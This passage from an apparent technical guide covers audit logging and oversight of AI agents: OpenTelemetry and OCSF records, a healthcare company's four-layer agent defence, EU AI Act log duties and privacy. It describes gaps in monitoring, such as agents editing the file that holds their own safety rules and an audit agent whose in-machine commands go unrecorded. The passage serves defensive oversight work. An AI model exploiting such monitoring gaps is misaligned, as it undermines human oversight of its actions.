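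If the proxy is on another machine, network equipment may replace the container's address and port on the way, and then the kernel and proxy records won't match. A separate proxy channel for each sandbox, as in Tracekit Box, at least identifies the sandbox.

**Shared identities.** OpenAI's agents used one login for the Artifactory server, so the server's records couldn't show which agent had made a request. The same problem can arise inside a single run, when an agent starts helper agents in its own container. Honeycomb, which sells monitoring software, advises customers to give each helper a distinct name, and its display labels any agent without one "Unknown". Names help with debugging, but hostile code may be able to change them. If it matters which helper opened a connection, each one needs its own sandbox and credentials from the supervisor.

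### OpenTelemetry and the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework

The example works because one operator chose all the field names. In practice, the harness, proxy and kernel probe often come from different suppliers. Two public formats are meant to give them a common vocabulary.

OpenTelemetry records each timed operation as a span and links related spans into a trace. Its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* defines an `invoke_agent` span, with fields for the agent's ID, name and version and for the conversation. Each tool call can have an `execute_tool` span, which should include the tool's name and, where available, an ID for the call, according to its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*. The arguments and the result are optional because they may contain sensitive data. With the default settings, the trace of the test-fixing job would show that the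 agent used its shell but not that it ran `pip install`.

These conventions are still changing. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, reports that they moved to a separate repository in June and that on August 21 they still had the status "Development" and no official release. An operator should store the version of the conventions with the records, because a search for a field's new name won't find records that use the old one. Wang also warns that the spans appear only if the agent's software produces them. Some common tools already do, including VS Code Copilot, the example in OpenTelemetry's *Inside the LLM Call*.

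The Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF) is a format for security events. It has standard event classes for activities such as starting a process or using the network, and "profiles" that add fields to those classes. AWS's *OCSF Achieves ITU Support* reports that version 1.8.0, released in March 2026, added a profile for AI operations. This profile describes the model and the context of a message. Tenzir's *message context* documents the context's role codes, which distinguish a user (1) from a model (2), a tool (3) and an agent (4).

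AWS's article, written by a director who led the founding of OCSF, presents OCSF as the basis for AI in security work. It says that member states of the International Telecommunication Union, a United Nations body, supported making OCSF an international standard by June 2026, and that OCSF's maintainers have begun working with OpenTelemetry's. For now, it makes sense to use OpenTelemetry for tool calls and OCSF for security events, with the same run ID and decision ID in both. The original software has to record those IDs, because neither format can supply missing ones.

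### Nine agents at a healthcare company

Maiti's account of a healthcare technology company shows how some of these tasks worked in practice. The company ran nine agents on the OpenClaw framework, each on its own virtual machine in Google's cloud. Maiti describes four layers of defence:

1. gVisor isolates each agent's programs.
2. A helper container holds the credentials.
3. Network rules limit each agent to approved destinations.
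4. A "prompt integrity framework" helps the model recognise who sent a message and which text it shouldn't trust.

The fourth layer wraps each incoming message in information about its sender, channel and time, which the framework supplies instead of the sender. It also labels users' text and tool results as untrusted, and adds five rules to the agent's standing instructions, such as asking the user when in doubt. Maiti calls this the most brittle layer because it works only if the model follows the instructions. In OpenClaw, agents can also edit the file that contains these rules.

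The dated steps in the paper's later sections cover 36 days, from February 3 to March 11, 2026, although its abstract reports results from a 90-day deployment with all four layers. The paper also describes the first three layers as the target of an unfinished move to Kubernetes. The machines went through three versions. The first had no firewall, the second added one and tightened file permissions, and the third logged outgoing connections and filtered DNS. The audit results therefore describe these machines more than the full design.

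Another agent, named Tony, carried out the audit on March 11. It searched for exposed credentials and loose file permissions, compared settings across the machines, and checked that each agent had the current prompt rules. It found four problems of high severity on three machines:

- twelve credentials in one agent's shell settings
- two configuration files that any program on the machine could read
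- an exposed key for Amazon's model service

Tony fixed all four the same day. Four medium-severity findings, all involving stray credential files, were still open when Maiti wrote. The other six machines had nothing above low severity.

Finding and fixing these problems within a day is a good result, but the repair may have been incomplete. Maiti doesn't report replacing the exposed keys. If they weren't replaced, any key that another program had already copied would still work. The procedure also saved backups of the shell settings it cleaned, which could still contain the keys.

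Tony is also the most attractive target in the fleet, because it can log in to every machine. Maiti limits its cloud permissions and sends its actions to a Google audit log that Tony can't alter. But that log covers administrative changes in the cloud, so commands that Tony runs after logging in to a machine need a separate record. Tony's network rules also permit access to the cloud metadata address, which can provide a machine's credentials. Maiti suggests replacing Tony with ordinary scanners, or separating the permission to scan from the permission to repair. An ordinary scanner seems better for most of this work, since checking file permissions doesn't require a language model.

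Maiti also compares the design with eleven case studies from the red-team study. Maiti claims in the abstract that the design covers all eleven, but in the conclusion that it covers nine. The paper's comparison lists eight that the layers address directly and one they address partly. Of the remaining two, one concerns the model's provider, and in the other the agents behaved well. Maiti doesn't report repeating the attacks against the finished system, so the claims rest on reasoning about the design. Maiti worked for Commure, a healthcare technology company, and founded another company, nFactor, so an independent test would be more convincing.

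### What the EU AI Act requires

Three articles of the EU's AI Act deal directly with logs, but only for systems it classifies as high-risk. Article 12 requires such a system to be able to record events automatically throughout its lifetime. The events must help identify risks and substantial modifications, support the provider's monitoring after the system is on the market, and allow the organisation using it to monitor its operation. The article prescribes no format and doesn't mention system calls. It sets minimum contents only for the logs of remote biometric identification systems, which must include the start and end of each use and the people who verified the results.

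Article 19 requires the provider, the company that develops the system or has it developed, to keep these logs if they are under its control. Article 26 requires the same of the deployer, the organisation that uses the system. Each must keep the logs for a period that suits the system's purpose and lasts at least six months, unless other EU or national law, particularly data protection law, provides otherwise. Financial institutions keep the logs with the records that financial law already requires.

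In addition to record storage, Article 26 requires the deployer to monitor the system and assign oversight to people with the necessary competence, training and authority. If the deployer has reason to think the system presents a risk, it must inform the provider and the authorities and suspend use.

These duties don't apply yet. The Omnibus, an amending law that entered into force on July 27, 2026, postponed them, according to the National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026). They will apply from December 2, 2027 to high-risk uses the Act lists, in areas such as hiring, education and credit, and from August 2, 2028 to AI in products that already fall under EU safety law, such as many medical devices.

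Many agents will never fall under these articles, because the classification depends mainly on the system's intended purpose. An agent that ranks job applicants would normally be high-risk, while the test-fixing agent normally wouldn't be, even though it can run any code. It's unclear whether the duty to keep a system's logs also covers logs from a proxy or kernel probe that the deployer added. Keeping those for the same six months would be a sensible precaution if privacy law allows it.

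Other laws can still apply. Maiti's agents were subject to HIPAA, the US health privacy law. Its security rule requires organisations to record and examine activity in systems that contain electronic patient data.

### Secrets, staff, storage and unread logs

A log with enough detail to explain everything an agent did will contain much of what the agent read. OpenTelemetry recommends leaving out instructions, messages and model output by default. For production systems that need them, it recommends storing the text separately, with its own access controls, and putting only a reference in the trace. An on-call engineer could then see the times, programs and destinations without access to the conversation.

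Masking and fingerprints can reduce the data in the main log. For example, when a command in Tracekit Box receives input that is known in advance, Ghosh records the input's size and SHA-256 hash, and includes the text only if it is 4 KiB or less. The hash lets an investigator check whether a suspected file was the input, but it gives weak protection to short or predictable data, such as a phone number, because someone could hash every possibility and compare the results.

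The records also contain information about the people who use agents. A log of prompts and tool calls shows when a developer works, what they don't know and how often they correct the agent. A company can limit this exposure by using run IDs in the everyday logs and keeping the owners' names in the register, which only incident responders and auditors may consult. It should tell staff what it records and rule out using the logs to assess their performance. If an employer used an AI system to evaluate developers from these logs, it could create a new legal problem, because the AI Act lists monitoring and evaluating workers among its high-risk uses.

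Storage is manageable if the operator is selective about what to keep. At the earlier estimate of 1,000 jobs a day, six months of process and connection records would take up about 165 GB. Adding every opened file would raise that to 7.5 TB, and adding every read and write to about 154 TB. The operator could sample routine file reads or delete them after a few days. Sampling is a bad idea for connections, decisions and uses of keys, because each missing record would either look like an unauthorised action or hide one. Conversation text could be deleted sooner than decisions, perhaps after 30 days, except for runs under investigation.

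Finally, people may not read the records. OpenAI's staff read the alert in June and still let the test continue, so the company must specify what the reviewer has to decide as well as when. Each agent's owner could be responsible for answering its alerts within a set time, with a deputy for absences and a deadline for every open finding. Someone should also review a few ordinary runs each week, because alerts cover only the problems that the rule writers expected. To test this arrangement, the company can occasionally have a harmless test agent attempt a forbidden connection and measure how long the run continues before a person or an automated control stops it.
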